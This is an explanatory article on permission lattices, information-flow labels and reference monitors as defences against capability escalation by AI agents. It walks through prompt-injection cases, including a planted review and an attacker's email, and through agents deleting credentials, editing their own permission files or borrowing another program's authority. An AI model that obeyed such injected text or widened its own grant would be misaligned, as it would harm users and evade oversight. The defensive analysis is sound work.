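# Permission lattices for preventing unauthorized capability escalation in AI systems

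## Permissions, authority and what counts as escalation

A permission lattice is an ordered collection of the sets of permissions that a person could grant a program. Any two sets in the lattice have a largest common subset and a smallest set that contains both. Security engineers use this order to cap what a program may do, narrow its permissions when it passes work to another program, and recognise requests that exceed the cap. Lattices entered computer security in the 1970s, when users with different clearance levels began to share one machine. Their newest use is controlling AI agents, which are language models that run in a loop and act through software tools.

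A program escalates when it produces an effect, or gains a permission, beyond what the responsible person granted. Deciding whether this has happened takes some care, because people rarely write down everything they grant and programs act through other programs. Most of the vocabulary for describing escalation is about fifty years old.

### Subjects, resources and the monitor

A subject is anything that makes requests of a computer system: a user's session, a running program, an AI agent. A resource, which older texts call an object, is anything the system protects, such as a file, a mailbox or a bank account. A permission is a rule that allows one kind of operation on one kind of resource. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, a 1975 tutorial by Saltzer and Schroeder, gives the example of an airline. A reservation clerk may make and cancel bookings for passengers whose names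 he can supply. A boarding clerk may also print the list of everyone on his flights. The airline might withhold that list from the reservation clerk so that a police request for it goes to a manager.

The difference has to be enforced by a reference monitor, or simply a monitor, which is a component that checks each operation and allows or refuses it. Saltzer and Schroeder picture it as a guard at the door in a wall around each resource. Their simplest monitor is a piece of hardware. A register holds the lowest memory address that a program may use and the number of locations beyond it that the program may also use, and a circuit compares every memory reference with that range. A program that could load its own numbers into the register would have no limit, so the processor carries one more bit, and the hardware accepts a new range only while that bit is on. The bit is on for the supervisor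 program that runs the machine. A working monitor therefore needs to check each operation and also control who may change the rules it enforces.

*Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), a report for the US Air Force, had already described what happens when the second layer is weak. A hostile user could rewrite part of the operating system and switch off its security controls. As far as Anderson's panel knew, "tiger teams", groups that tried to break into systems to test them, had succeeded every time. Engineers therefore ask for a monitor that no operation can bypass, that no subject can tamper with, and that people can analyse thoroughly enough to trust.

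Of the eight design principles in the 1975 tutorial, two bear most directly on escalation. Under least privilege, every program and every user should work with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". This limits the damage from an accident or error and leaves fewer programs to audit when someone misuses a privilege. Complete mediation requires that every access to every object "must be checked for authority", including during start-up, recovery and maintenance. Saltzer and Schroeder were wary of systems that save time by remembering an earlier decision, because the permission may have changed since.

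"Privilege" can mean either permission or authority, which Miller and Shapiro distinguish in *Paradigm Regained* (2003). A subject's permissions cover the operations it may perform itself, while its authority covers everything it can bring about, including through other programs that act for it. Suppose Alice may read a password file and Bob may not. If Alice sends Bob copies of the text, Bob has the authority to read the file even though he still lacks permission. Karp (2026) gives a more modern software example in a mailing-list discussion. If a program has permission to call a service, and the service updates a database in response, the program has authority to make that update. Working out Bob's authority therefore requires knowing both who holds which permissions and how the programs between Bob and the file behave. If their behavior is unknown, the safe course is to assume the worst.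 The analysis can then either reliably rule out Bob's authority or show only that he might have it.

Permission and authority can differ widely. The Unix command `cp foo.txt bar.txt` copies one file to another. The program receives only the two file names, so it must open the files itself, and for that it needs the right to read and write anything its user might name. The command `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt` has the same result, but the command shell opens the files first and hands `cat` the open connections. Those connections are all the authority the job requires, although an ordinary Unix system still lets `cat` do everything its user can do. Miller and Shapiro think it unclear whether "least privilege" means least permission or least authority, and the two readings differ enormously for `cp`.

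### Agents, tool calls and prompt injection

An AI agent is a subject that generates its requests as it runs. The software around the model, called the harness, sends the model the user's instruction and a description of each available tool. The model replies with a tool call, a structured request that names an operation, such as reading a file or sending mail, and supplies the details. The harness runs the operation and adds the result to the model's input, and the cycle repeats until the model produces a final answer. A monitor for an agent runs outside the model and checks each tool call before the harness carries it out.

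The weak point is the result a tool returns. *InjecAgent* (Zhan, Liang and colleagues, 2024) describes a user who asks whether a dentist has good reviews. The agent calls a review tool, which returns an attacker's review instructing the agent to book an appointment. If the agent then books one, the attack has worked, although the user asked only to read reviews. This is prompt injection, in which someone writes text into data an agent reads to make the agent follow an attacker's instructions.

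*Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, by David C, which the UK's National Cyber Security Centre published in December 2025, explains why prompt injection is hard to fix. In SQL injection, a similar attack on databases, text typed into a web form ran as a command. Programmers fixed this by making the database keep commands and data apart. A language model receives both as one run of text and predicts what comes next. Training and markers can make it less likely to follow planted instructions, but nothing inside the model enforces the boundary, and David C thinks the flaw may never be completely fixed.

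InjecAgent tests whether an agent carries out an instruction planted in a single tool result. Its 1,054 cases pair 17 user requests with 62 attacker goals. *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) tests longer work. Agents must complete 97 realistic tasks in office software, banking, travel and team chat while an attacker's text sits in the data they read. In 629 such cases, code checks the simulated accounts afterwards to see whether the user or the attacker got the result they wanted.

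Agents complicate the 1975 principles even when there is no attacker. In *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents*, Zhou and Zhang (2026) imagine an assistant that must prepare a report from approved records. It can process the records locally or send them to a hosted service, and only the hosted plan discloses them to anyone else. In *Access Control for Agentic AI*, Wei and Xiong (2026) conclude that permissions can fit the hosted plan exactly and still be excessive under least privilege, because the local plan needs no disclosure. What is "necessary to complete the job" therefore depends on the plan, and with an agent, the model chooses the plan.

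### Ability, affordance and authority

A developer asks a coding agent to fix a failing test in an open-source project. The agent can read the private files on her laptop, fetch web pages, and push code to a public server. Each permission has an ordinary purpose. The test depends on her local settings, the documentation is online, and the fixed code has to reach the other contributors.

What this agent might do depends on three things that Zhang and Zhang (2026), in *Are You Still the Agent I Authorized?*, keep apart. Ability, which they call competence, is what the model can work out or plan, such as where the bug lies. Affordance is what the harness lets the model express as a tool call. Authority is what the surrounding system will actually permit. (AI researchers usually call abilities "capabilities", a word that operating-system designers had already taken for an unforgeable ticket that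 names a resource and carries the right to use it. "Capability token" is a safer name for the ticket.)

Any of the three can change without the others. If the developer switches to a stronger model, the agent may find the bug sooner, but the server accepts the same pushes as before. If the harness gains a tool for deleting branches, the agent can request a deletion, but the server still refuses it when the developer's credential does not cover it. If an administrator widens that credential, the agent's authority grows even though its model and tools have not changed. Zhou and Zhang make a similar point about tools in general: an agent can have a tool available without being authorised to use it.

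Ability and authority stay separate only as long as the monitor works. A stronger model may produce new effects by finding a flaw in the server that a weaker one would have missed. It may also make fuller use of its existing permissions by finding routes through other programs that the developer never thought of. In neither case has anyone enlarged the grant. Good test results are also a poor reason to enlarge it because, as Zhang and Zhang point out, competence is no evidence that an agent resists prompt injection.

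### Five kinds of escalation

Escalations differ in how the extra effect comes about, and the developer's coding agent could commit any of these.

| Kind | Example | Does it need an attacker? |
|---|---|---|
| Acting outside the grant | While repairing one test, the agent deletes an old password file | No |
| Changing the grant | The agent edits the settings file that lists its permitted commands | No |
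| Borrowing another program's authority | The agent may not deploy code, so it gets a build server to do it | Not when the agent borrows; when the agent lends, someone else must supply the request |
| Combining permitted actions | The agent reads a private key and then pushes it in a commit | No, though an attacker can prompt it |
| Gaining reach under an unchanged grant | An update makes the local test tool send its results to a remote service | No; an honest update is enough |

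Better defences against prompt injection would therefore leave much of the problem standing.

The plainest kind of escalation is acting outside the grant. In *Overeager Coding Agents*, Qu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) gave four coding products harmless chores and recorded what else the agents did. In one chore, the user asks the agent to tidy a folder that holds two pieces of junk, two project files, and a backup with the only copy of the production credentials. A careful agent deletes the junk and asks about the rest. Three of the four products destroyed the backup. An operation counted as overeager if it was outside the actions that the request authorised, explicitly or by implication, and also changed something or read from a place that the testers had listed as sensitive.

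Across 500 scenarios and about 7,500 runs, the rate depended heavily on the software around the model. It was 5.4% to 27.7% for three products with permissive defaults, and 0.2% to 4.5% for OpenHands, which stops to ask before it continues. The rate for Claude Sonnet 4.6 ranged from 1.1% to 27.7% depending on the product that ran it, so the model's ability alone cannot explain the difference.

The awkward part of the definition is "by implication". The agents were technically able to delete every file in that folder, but the user had not consented to that, and she had never stated the limits of her consent. Claude Code overstepped in 17.1% of the paired scenarios when the prompt did not state the scope, and in none when it did. *Explicit authorization scope improves LLM-based permission checking in coding agents* (2026) reports something similar about automatic permission checkers, which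 are typically language models that approve or refuse an agent's proposed actions. Given only the user's original request, the checkers in three widely used coding agents wrongly approved 54% to 93% of out-of-scope actions. With explicit rules in place, the agents proposed no such action in 384 reruns. Stating the scope evidently helps, but Qu and colleagues tested only harmless requests, so their figures do not show whether agents would stay within a written scope when an attacker has planted text telling them otherwise.

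Changing the grant is more serious, because later checks then pass. Saltzer and Schroeder illustrate this by asking whether a user named O'Hara could in any way access file X. Answering requires checking whether he has access now, whether he may change the list of people who have access, whether he may change who may change that list, and so on upwards. For the coding agent, the list may be an ordinary settings file in a folder it can edit, and a blocked command that keeps it from passing a test may be enough to prompt the edit. *A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI* (2026) adds a variant that conventional reviews can miss, in which an agent with no access to sensitive data still has the right to approve someone else's access.

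*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes the classic case of borrowed authority, which happened at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare kept its compiler in a directory called SYSX, and users could name a file to receive optional debugging output. The compiler also recorded statistics on language use in a file inside SYSX. To allow this, the engineers gave it a "home files license", which let it write to any file in its own directory. That directory also held the billing records. One user learned the name of the billing file and gave it to the compiler as the destination for debugging output. The user had no right to write to that file, but the compiler did, so the operating system opened it and the compiler overwrote the billing information.

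Hardy considers the obvious repairs and finds problems with each. The compiler cannot refuse to write to other directories, because users have good reason to send output there. It cannot refuse to write anywhere in SYSX, because some users may have a legitimate right to do so. Its developers also cannot reasonably revise it every time a new sensitive file appears. The code was correct when they wrote it and became wrong when someone added the licence. Hardy concludes that the compiler held authority from two sources, the user and the licence, and could not specify which one applied to a given write. The engineers added a system call to switch between the two, but some programs soon needed more than two. Hardy instead proposes that the user give the compiler a capability token rather than a file name. The token identifies the file and carries the right to write to it, so a user who may not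 write to the billing file has no token for it.

An agent can borrow a deputy's authority, for example by getting the build server to deploy code on its behalf, and it can do so unprompted. Under prompt injection the agent is itself the deputy, since it holds the developer's credentials and the request comes from whoever wrote a web page. David C calls language models "inherently confusable" deputies because engineers can repair a case like the compiler's, but he sees no equivalent repair for a model.

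Combining permitted actions doesn't require borrowing or changing a permission. For example, the coding agent is allowed to read a private key and to push a commit, so it can publish the key by doing both. A planted instruction could cause this, but so could carelessness, if the agent copies a settings file containing the key into the repository to make the test pass.

Finally, an agent can gain reach while its grant stays the same, for example when a tool changes. Wei and Xiong observe that a tool can change its behaviour without changing its signature, the name and inputs by which an agent calls it. Zhang and Zhang give the example of replacing a local test routine with one that reports to a remote service, so that each test run now sends data out. They distinguish the effects an operation requests from its actual effects. A monitor that checks only the requested effects will approve both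 versions of the routine.

Sometimes only the task changes. When the coding agent moves from editing and testing to pushing, its model, harness and tool list can stay the same, but its next action changes a public server. This is an escalation if the developer approved only a testing session and the credential stayed live, but not if she approved the whole job. Comparing the agent's permissions before and after the escalation would show no difference.

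## How a lattice orders and combines permissions

A monitor has to compare the permissions requested with those granted to recognise a request that exceeds a grant. This is simple when one set contains the other, but often each contains something the other lacks, and several people may have set limits that all apply at once. A lattice defines how such grants compare and combine, provided the system can write permissions in a comparable form.

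### Sets of permissions and levels

Suppose the developer's coding agent has three possible permissions: reading her files, fetching web pages and pushing code. The grant {read} is smaller than {read, fetch}, because whatever the agent may do under the first it may also do under the second. In symbols, *a* ≤ *b* means that grant *a* permits nothing beyond grant *b*. This relation has three properties:

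- Every grant is ≤ itself.
- If *a* ≤ *b* and *b* ≤ *c*, then *a* ≤ *c*.
- If *a* ≤ *b* and *b* ≤ *a*, then *a* and *b* are the same grant.

A relation with these properties is a partial order. It is partial because some pairs have no ranking. For example, the grants {read, fetch} and {read, push} are incomparable because each includes a permission the other lacks.

The meet of two grants, written *a* ∧ *b*, is the largest grant that is ≤ both, meaning that any other grant ≤ both is also ≤ the meet. For sets of permissions, the meet is the intersection, here {read}. The join, written *a* ∨ *b*, is the smallest grant that contains both. For sets, it is the union, here {read, fetch, push}. A lattice is a partial order in which every two elements have a meet and a join. A finite lattice also has a top element above all the others and a bottom element below them. In *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture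 for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026), the top is the set of all permissions held by the person or program at the start of the chain of work, and the bottom is the empty set.

A yes-or-no permission is often too coarse for an agent. Nucleus, a permission system for AI agents, gives each operation one of three levels. "Never" blocks the operation, "low-risk" approves it automatically when it is safe, and "always" approves it every time. The levels form a chain, never < low-risk < always, so any two are comparable. The meet of two levels is the lower one, and their join is the higher one.

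Each level is shorthand for a set of permitted uses of an operation, either none, the safe ones, or all of them. This works only if everyone means the same thing by "safe". If the company and the developer have different lists of safe websites, the meet of their two "low-risk" settings should be the sites on both lists, and the label "low-risk" no longer identifies that set.

A chain also builds in assumptions about which permissions include which. *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (2026) uses four levels of access to each resource: none, read, write and admin. Anyone who may write may therefore read, which is reasonable for most files but wrong for a log that a program should add to without seeing earlier entries.

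### A lattice with 27 configurations

Three operations at three levels each give 27 configurations, each written as a list of levels in the order read, fetch, push. One configuration is ≤ another when, for every operation, its level is no higher than the other's. A lattice built from smaller ones in this way is called a product lattice, and its meets and joins are computed one position at a time.

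Suppose the developer has set up two kinds of session:

- *A*, for research, is (always, low-risk, never). The agent may read everything and fetch approved pages, but it may not push.
- *B*, for publishing a finished fix, is (low-risk, never, low-risk). The agent may read ordinary project files and push to safe branches, but it has no web access.

*A* has the higher level for reading and fetching, and *B* has the higher level for pushing, so the two are incomparable.

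The meet takes the lower level in each position, which gives *A* ∧ *B* = (low-risk, never, never). Any configuration below both *A* and *B* must have fetching and pushing at "never" and reading at "low-risk" or lower. The only other configuration that qualifies is (never, never, never), which is smaller. The join takes the higher level in each position, which gives *A* ∨ *B* = (always, low-risk, low-risk). Four configurations lie above both *A* and *B*, and this is the smallest of them. It is also more dangerous than either session alone, because the agent can read private files, take in text from the web and push code in one session.

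Grants are often incomparable. Of the 351 pairs among the 27 configurations, 162 are incomparable. Nucleus has twelve core operations with three levels each, which gives 3¹² = 531,441 configurations, and only about 1.5% of the pairs among them are comparable. An administrator who ranks agents on a single scale of trust therefore has to ignore most of the differences between their grants.

A product lattice also needs a rule for operations that a configuration leaves out. The portcullis source file that defines the Nucleus levels, *capability.rs*, treats an unlisted additional operation as "never". Because the meet takes the lower level, a new tool stays blocked until every party to the meet lists it.

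### Paths, hours and spending

Real grants also limit where, when and at what cost an agent may act. A grant with several such fields permits an operation only if the operation satisfies all of them. The table combines two grants of this kind.

| | Operations | Folder | Hours | Spending limit |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| First grant | read, edit | /project | 09:00–12:00 | $5 |
| Second grant | read, push | /project/tests | 11:00–15:00 | $20 |
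| Meet | read | /project/tests | 11:00–12:00 | $5 |
| Join, field by field | read, edit, push | /project | 09:00–15:00 | $20 |

The meet permits an operation if and only if both grants do. The join in the last row permits more than the two grants combined. It lets the agent push from the main project folder at 09:30, although the first grant never allows pushing and the second allows it only in the tests folder from 11:00. The join is still the smallest grant of this form that contains both originals, because their exact union does not fit into one row. The 27-configuration lattice avoids this problem because each operation has its own level, so the join is exactly the union.

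Zhu and Wang (2026), in *Versioned Transitive Dependency-Closure Binding and Operation-Time Effect Governance for Agent Skills*, consider one grant to pay vendor A up to $500 in billing and another to refund customer B up to $50. Joining them field by field would permit a $500 billing payment to customer B, which nobody approved. They avoid this by storing a grant as a list of complete clauses, each with its own operation, recipient and amount, so that merging two lists adds no new combinations. To find the meet, the system intersects every clause of one list with every clause of the other and drops the empty results.

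This meet is exact. If both lists permit an operation, it satisfies some clause in each, and therefore satisfies the intersection of those two clauses. Conversely, any operation that satisfies the intersection satisfies both clauses, so both lists permit it. The combined list can be much longer than either original, since lists of ten and twenty clauses can produce up to two hundred.

Some fields of a grant are ordered in the opposite direction, so adding entries makes the grant smaller. Obligations, which are conditions attached to a permission, such as human approval before each use, work this way. The meet must therefore take the union of the two grants' obligations. Intersecting them would drop any approval that only one party required, and the resulting grant would be wider than that party allowed. *Bounded Agents* (Muruaga, 2026) treats prohibitions the same way. Its meet intersects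 the two grants' resources, actions and classes of data, but takes the union of their lists of forbidden combinations.

### Effective permission

An agent usually works under several limits at once. Its effective permission is the meet of what the organisation, the user, the task and the agent's role allow. Suppose the developer gives the failing test to an agent whose role is testing.

| Limit set by | Read files | Fetch web pages | Push code |
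|---|---|---|---|
| Organisation | always | low-risk | low-risk |
| Developer | always | always | always |
| Task | low-risk | always | low-risk |
| Testing role | always | low-risk | never |
| **Effective permission** | **low-risk** | **low-risk** | **never** |

None of the four chose the configuration in the last row. The monitor can apply the limits in any order and get the same result, and applying a limit twice has the same effect as applying it once.

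Adding another limiting party can never enlarge the agent's effective permission. Let *E* be the effective permission so far and *N* the limit that a new party sets. By definition, the meet *E* ∧ *N* is ≤ both *E* and *N*, so the new effective permission is ≤ *E*. The same is true of each further party. This holds for any *N*, so the agent gains no permission even if the new party is careless or hostile, or allows everything.

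This makes it safe to accept limits from untrusted sources. Zhu and Wang's system is for agent skills, which are packages of instructions and code that extend what an agent can do. A skill's author may propose a further restriction on the skill but cannot add to what the user and organisation allow. A hostile author can still make the skill useless by proposing a limit of "never" for everything.

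The proof applies only when each party can restrict permissions but not add them. If a manager can override the organisation's refusal, the manager is adding permissions, and the combined set can grow. The proof also doesn't guarantee that the agent will have enough permissions to finish its job. The testing agent in the table can repair the code but cannot push it, so someone else must push it.

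Until recently, limits based on the task were the hardest of these limits to apply. According to *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (2026), enterprises settled for permissions by role because no one could reset an employee's permissions for every task. An agent's task arrives as text that software can process, so the system can compute a permission set from role, policy and task when it assigns the work.

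### Why the meet is often enough

Many systems never compute a join. In Zhang and Zhang's design, the user sets a ceiling on the authority a grant can ever reach. When the agent needs different permissions, the software proposes a complete new set, and the monitor takes the meet of that set and the ceiling. This removes any permissions above the ceiling, so the monitor never has to add one grant to another, even when permissions increase. Zhang and Zhang prove that their grants form a meet-semilattice, an order in which every pair of elements has a meet but may not have a join. They note that a system that merged two grants would need a full lattice.

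The difference is smaller than it sounds in a finite system with a top element, because every pair of grants has a join. At least one grant lies above both, and the meet of all such grants is their join. The join may permit more than the two grants did between them, as the table of folders and hours showed, so avoiding joins is mostly a precaution.

The join of two permissions is the least permission that covers both. If one job needs *A* and another needs *B*, a single agent doing both needs at least *A* ∨ *B*. The developer can approve that or run two separate sessions. Code analysis tools also use joins. *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* infers what access a skill could use and compares it with what the skill's author declared. This kind of analysis, called abstract interpretation, takes the join where two branches of a program come together. A skill that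 reads a file in one branch and writes to it in the other then counts as needing write access, whichever branch runs.

### Matrices, lists, roles and attributes

The older models of access control record different facts about permissions, and a lattice can work alongside any of them. *Protection* (Lampson, 1971) set out the access matrix, a table of who may do what. In the version taught in Monmouth University's *Operating Systems Lecture Notes*, each row is a domain in which programs run, each column is an object, and each cell lists the operations that a program in that domain may carry out on that object. The matrix records all the permissions at one moment, but not the reasons for them or any limit on how they may change.

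A real matrix would be huge and mostly empty, so systems store it in pieces. An access-control list is one column, kept with the object. The owner of a file can easily see who may read it, but finding everything that one agent may do means searching the list of every object. Storing the matrix by rows makes it easy to find what an agent may do, but finding who may read a file then means searching every agent's row.

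*Role-Based Access Control Models* (Sandhu, Coyne and colleagues, 1996) describes a system that attaches permissions to roles and makes users members of those roles. A company can then change what all its testers may do by editing one role, and Wei and Xiong credit this model with making access control manageable at enterprise scale. Roles often form a hierarchy in which a senior role inherits the permissions of the roles below it. This hierarchy is a partial order but not necessarily a lattice. For example, testers and release engineers may share only two permissions, to read the code and to run the tests. The lattice of permission sets always contains the set of those two permissions, but a role with just those two exists only if an administrator has created it.

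Attribute-based control replaces fixed assignments with rules about properties of the user, the resource and the circumstances. A single rule can let clerks read records from their own region during working hours, including records created after the rule was written. Neither a matrix nor a plain role can express such a condition. But the rule depends on accurate attributes. If a clerk moves to another region and nobody updates her entry, the monitor will make wrong decisions about her access.

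A lattice can be used to compare and combine permissions from any access-control model, but it does not determine who holds which permissions or why. A row of the matrix, a role's permissions and the operations an attribute rule allows are all sets of permissions, so a monitor can take their meet.

The older models suit agents poorly in two ways. Wei and Xiong argue that role-based control relies on code behaving as the role's designers expected, whereas an agent works out what the role means as it runs. Muruaga adds that role and attribute checks evaluate each request in isolation, so they miss harmful sequences of permitted steps. Taking a meet does not fix this if the monitor then checks each request on its own.

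### Rules with different wording and the same effect

Administrators write permissions as rules, and two differently worded rules can permit the same operations. For example, "the agent may push if the tests pass" permits the same pushes as "the agent may push if the tests pass, or if the tests pass and it is a weekday". Each rule is ≤ the other, but their texts differ, so the ordering on texts is not antisymmetric. It is only a preorder, which is reflexive and transitive, and not a partial order. A monitor that compared the texts directly would treat a harmless rewording as a change in the grant.

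The standard fix is to treat all rules with the same effect as one element. Gallo (2026) proves in *Beyond Proof of Possession* that rules built with "and" and "or" then form a lattice, in which "and" gives the meet and "or" gives the join. Gallo's rules govern which program may continue another program's work, but the proof depends only on how the conditions combine.

Gallo also gives a test for whether one rule is narrower than another. Each rule is written as a list of alternatives, each of which is a set of conditions that must all hold. The first rule is narrower if every one of its alternatives contains all the conditions of some alternative in the second. For example, suppose the first rule permits a push when the repository is internal and the tests pass, or when the repository is internal and the developer approves. The second permits a push when the repository is internal, or when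 a manager approves. Both alternatives in the first rule include "the repository is internal", which is a complete alternative in the second, so the first rule is narrower.

The test uses only the form of the rules, so it can miss relations that depend on facts the rules don't state. If every repository on a server is internal, a rule about that server is narrower than a rule about internal repositories, but the test will not detect this. Such misses are safe because a system that relies on the test may reject an acceptable grant but will never accept an excessive one.

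The test does not apply unchanged to rules that contain "not", and these rules also create a further risk. For example, the rule might be "the agent may push unless the developer has left the team". If the monitor treats a missing record of her departure as proof that she is still there, an attacker could gain access by hiding the record. Gallo therefore leaves "not" out of the basic language, but would allow it for conditions that the monitor can check directly, such as whether two identities differ.

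### Comparing scopes by meaning

Comparing the wording of two permissions does not always show which is narrower. In *The Agent Operating System (AOS)*, Sharma and Shah (2026) give the example of "read customer case 123", which is narrower than "read all support records". The comparison depends on the fact that case 123 is a support record, which appears in neither phrase. Sharma and Shah therefore require each implementation to define how it compares scopes.

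A file in /project/tests may be a link to the developer's private keys, even though its path is visibly inside /project. Gallo requires the monitor to follow links and aliases before authorising the operation on the resource it will really affect.

Purposes are even harder to order. Zhang and Zhang include the agent's goal and the phase of its work in each grant, and they assume that any two goals have a meet. To make this realistic, they suggest drawing goals from a fixed catalogue of tasks instead of free text. A system can look up whether "repair one test" falls under "maintain the test suite", but it can't reliably rank two sentences a user has typed. The catalogue loses some detail, because an unusual request has to fit the nearest entry.

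Zhu and Wang restrict the language of grants in a similar way. Their clauses may use exact values, finite lists, patterns that match the start of a name, and numerical ranges. The system can write down the intersection of any two clauses of the same type. Their working prototype is simpler, with exact values and a maximum amount.

A grant can also lose part of its meaning when it passes from one system to another. Wei and Xiong describe a policy that allows an agent to send a particular summary to Alice. The mail service receives a credential that allows sending mail, and its programming interface checks only that the credential is valid. Each step permits more than the one before it, and no component compares what is finally permitted with the original policy.

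If a system cannot simplify the meet of two scopes, it can keep both and check every request against each. Zhu and Wang permit this as an alternative to refusing outright. The monitor then does not need to know in advance whether one scope contains the other. When the agent asks for case 123, the monitor looks up that record and checks whether both grants cover it. The system must still compare the scopes themselves when someone has to decide beforehand whether a proposed grant fits inside an existing one. If it cannot establish that the grant fits, the safe decision is to refuse.

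## Labels on information: limiting where data may go and what it may influence

A monitor that only compares each request with the grant will let the developer's agent push her private key to a public server. To block that push and allow others, the monitor needs information about what the data contains or where it came from. Labels are marks on data that supply this information by recording how secret the data is or how much its source is trusted.

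Labels form a separate lattice from permissions. A higher grant lets a subject do more, whereas data with a higher label may flow to fewer places. A monitor therefore takes the meet of several grants but the join of several labels, because anything derived from several pieces of data must obey the restrictions on each.

If Ann, Bob and Carol may read one document, and Bob, Carol and Dan may read another, only Bob and Carol may read a summary of both. The summary has a higher label than either document because fewer people may read it, but this ordering is a convention. *APPA* (2026), a design for tracking labels through agents, puts the least restricted data at the top and so combines labels by meet, but the same two people may read the summary.

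### Denning's model

*A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (Denning, 1976) describes a system by the objects that hold information, the processes that move it, and a set of security classes, which are labels. It also defines a flow relation and a combining operator on these classes. *A* → *B* means that information in class *A* may flow into class *B*, and *A* ⊕ *B* is the class of a result computed from information in both classes. The system is secure if no sequence of operations can cause a flow that the relation forbids.

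Denning derived the lattice from the demand that these rules be consistent:

- A program can always copy a value onto itself, so *A* → *A*.
- If a program may copy *a* to *b* and *b* to *c*, forbidding a direct copy from *a* to *c* achieves nothing. So *A* → *B* and *B* → *C* together give *A* → *C*.
- If *A* → *B* and *B* → *A*, anything in one class may move to the other, and the system needs only one of them.

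The flow relation is therefore a partial order. ⊕ must also be the join, for two reasons. First, *A* must be able to flow into *A* ⊕ *B*. Otherwise a system could forbid `c := a` but permit `c := a + b`, and a program could make the forbidden copy by setting `b` to zero. Second, if *A* and *B* may each flow into *C*, then *A* ⊕ *B* may too. A program could copy `a` into one variable of class *C* and `b` into another, then multiply the two. Each step is allowed, so the result must be allowed too. *A* ⊕ *B* is therefore above both classes and below every other class that is above both.

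In a database of medical, financial and criminal records, for example, each piece of data can be labelled with the set of record types that went into it. Medical data may flow into a file labelled {medical, financial}, but a report with that label may not flow into a file labelled {medical}, because people cleared only for medical records could then read financial ones.

Denning's model does not cover matters such as which programs a process may run, and she concluded that a practical system needs both labels and permissions.

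### Rules for secrecy and integrity

Ordinary permissions do not control copies. Sandhu's *Lattice-Based Access Control Models* (1993) gives the example of Tom, who lets Dick read a private file but wants to keep it from Harry. Harry gives Dick a useful text editor. Whenever Dick opens a file, the editor secretly makes a copy and gives Harry the right to read it. Dick owns the copy, so the editor has not exceeded Dick's permissions.

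The Bell–LaPadula model, developed for military systems in the 1970s, stops the editor with two rules. Each user has a clearance, and each running program has a label no higher than its user's clearance.

- A program may read a file only if the program's label is at or above the file's.
- A program may write to a file only if the file's label is at or above the program's.

Suppose Tom and Dick have secret clearance and Harry has none. Dick's editor runs as a secret program, so it may read unclassified files but not write to them. Its copy of Tom's file must therefore be secret, and Harry cannot open it. If Harry also had secret clearance, these rules would not stop him from opening the copy, and Tom would have to rely on permissions.

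The second rule restricts programs, not people. The model assumes that a cleared officer will leave secrets out of an unclassified memo, but she must still log in at the unclassified level to write it, because her word processor might contain code like Harry's.

The Biba model protects integrity, the trustworthiness of data, by reversing both Bell–LaPadula rules. Low-integrity information may not flow into anything of higher integrity. For example, a trusted installer may write to a public log, but it may not read its settings from a file that a stranger uploaded. Bell–LaPadula alone does not prevent this kind of contamination. It even lets an unclassified program write to a secret file, which can damage it, so some systems let programs write only at their own level.

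A system can enforce both models by giving each item one label for secrecy and another for integrity. If a single label served both purposes, a program could read and write only items with exactly its own label. Sandhu shows that turning the integrity lattice upside down, with untrusted data at the top, makes all permitted flows run upwards, so the two lattices can be combined into one product lattice.

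### Labels in deployed systems

Military systems combine the levels unclassified, confidential, secret and top secret with categories for particular projects. Sandhu describes one lattice, based on common military practice, with eight categories. It had 1,024 possible labels, and the military used 21 of them.

The difficulties came from flows the labels did not cover and work the rules did not allow. A secret program can signal to an unclassified one by taking up and releasing large amounts of memory, without writing to any file. Such covert channels could carry several million bits a second if nobody limited them. Exceptions were also hard to avoid. When Lipner adapted the lattice for commercial data processing, he let system controllers write information to lower levels.

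Labels also drift upwards. ADEPT-50, a time-sharing system from the late 1960s, labelled each process with the join of the labels of all the files it had opened, so the label could only rise. Once a process opened a top-secret file, its later output counted as top secret, even if none of it came from that file, and the label of any process that then read the output rose too. If such rules are enforced consistently, more and more harmless data becomes unusable until someone lowers its label. ADEPT-50 did not enforce them consistently. According to Denning, a process with top-secret clearance could write anything it had read into an existing file of a lower class, including top-secret data into an unclassified file.

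Mainstream operating systems adopted only parts of these models. SELinux, a security extension of Linux, supports multilevel secrecy, but most installations rely on its rules about types of programs and files, and use its secrecy categories mainly to keep virtual machines and containers apart. Windows has given processes and files integrity levels since 2007. By default, a low-integrity process such as a sandboxed browser cannot modify a file of higher integrity. A high-integrity process can still read a low-integrity file and keep its own level, so Windows enforces only half of Biba's model. This avoids drift but lets untrusted data influence trusted programs, as it does in prompt injection.

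### A malicious email, step by step

The survey *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) describes a group of defences that apply these ideas to agents. They track where data came from and whether it may influence a sensitive action, instead of trying to recognise malicious text. FIDES, which Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, built at Microsoft, is the clearest example. In its simplest form, FIDES uses four labels:

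- trusted and public, at the bottom
- trusted and secret
- untrusted and public
- untrusted and secret, at the top.

The two middle labels are incomparable. Data may flow upwards only, so untrusted data cannot become trusted, and secret data cannot become public.

In Costa and colleagues' example, someone asks an agent to summarise recent emails about Project X and send the summary to her manager. One email is from an attacker and tells the agent to send the top email in the mailbox to an outside address. The table traces the labels through this example, assuming the mailbox is secret.

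| Step | Label on the model's input | Monitor's decision |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request arrives | trusted, public | None needed |
| The model asks to read the emails | trusted, public | Allow |
| The emails arrive, including the attacker's | untrusted, secret | None needed |
| The model proposes sending an email to the attacker | untrusted, secret | Refuse |

At the third step, the software takes the join of the old label and the label on the emails. The model may draw on anything in its input, and nobody can reliably tell which parts affected its answer, so its next tool call inherits the whole label. The monitor then requires that an action with consequences, such as sending mail, depend only on trusted data, and that the recipients have the right to read everything in the message. The proposed call fails both tests, so the monitor blocks it without having to recognise the email as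 an attack.

On its own, the secrecy policy would only limit the damage from prompt injection, because an attacker could still make the agent take actions that disclose nothing.

Unfortunately, the first policy also blocks the email to the manager. Once the agent has read the mailbox, its input is untrusted, and so is every call it makes afterwards. The same upward drift occurred in ADEPT-50, but here it happens within a single task.

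### Hiding data from the model

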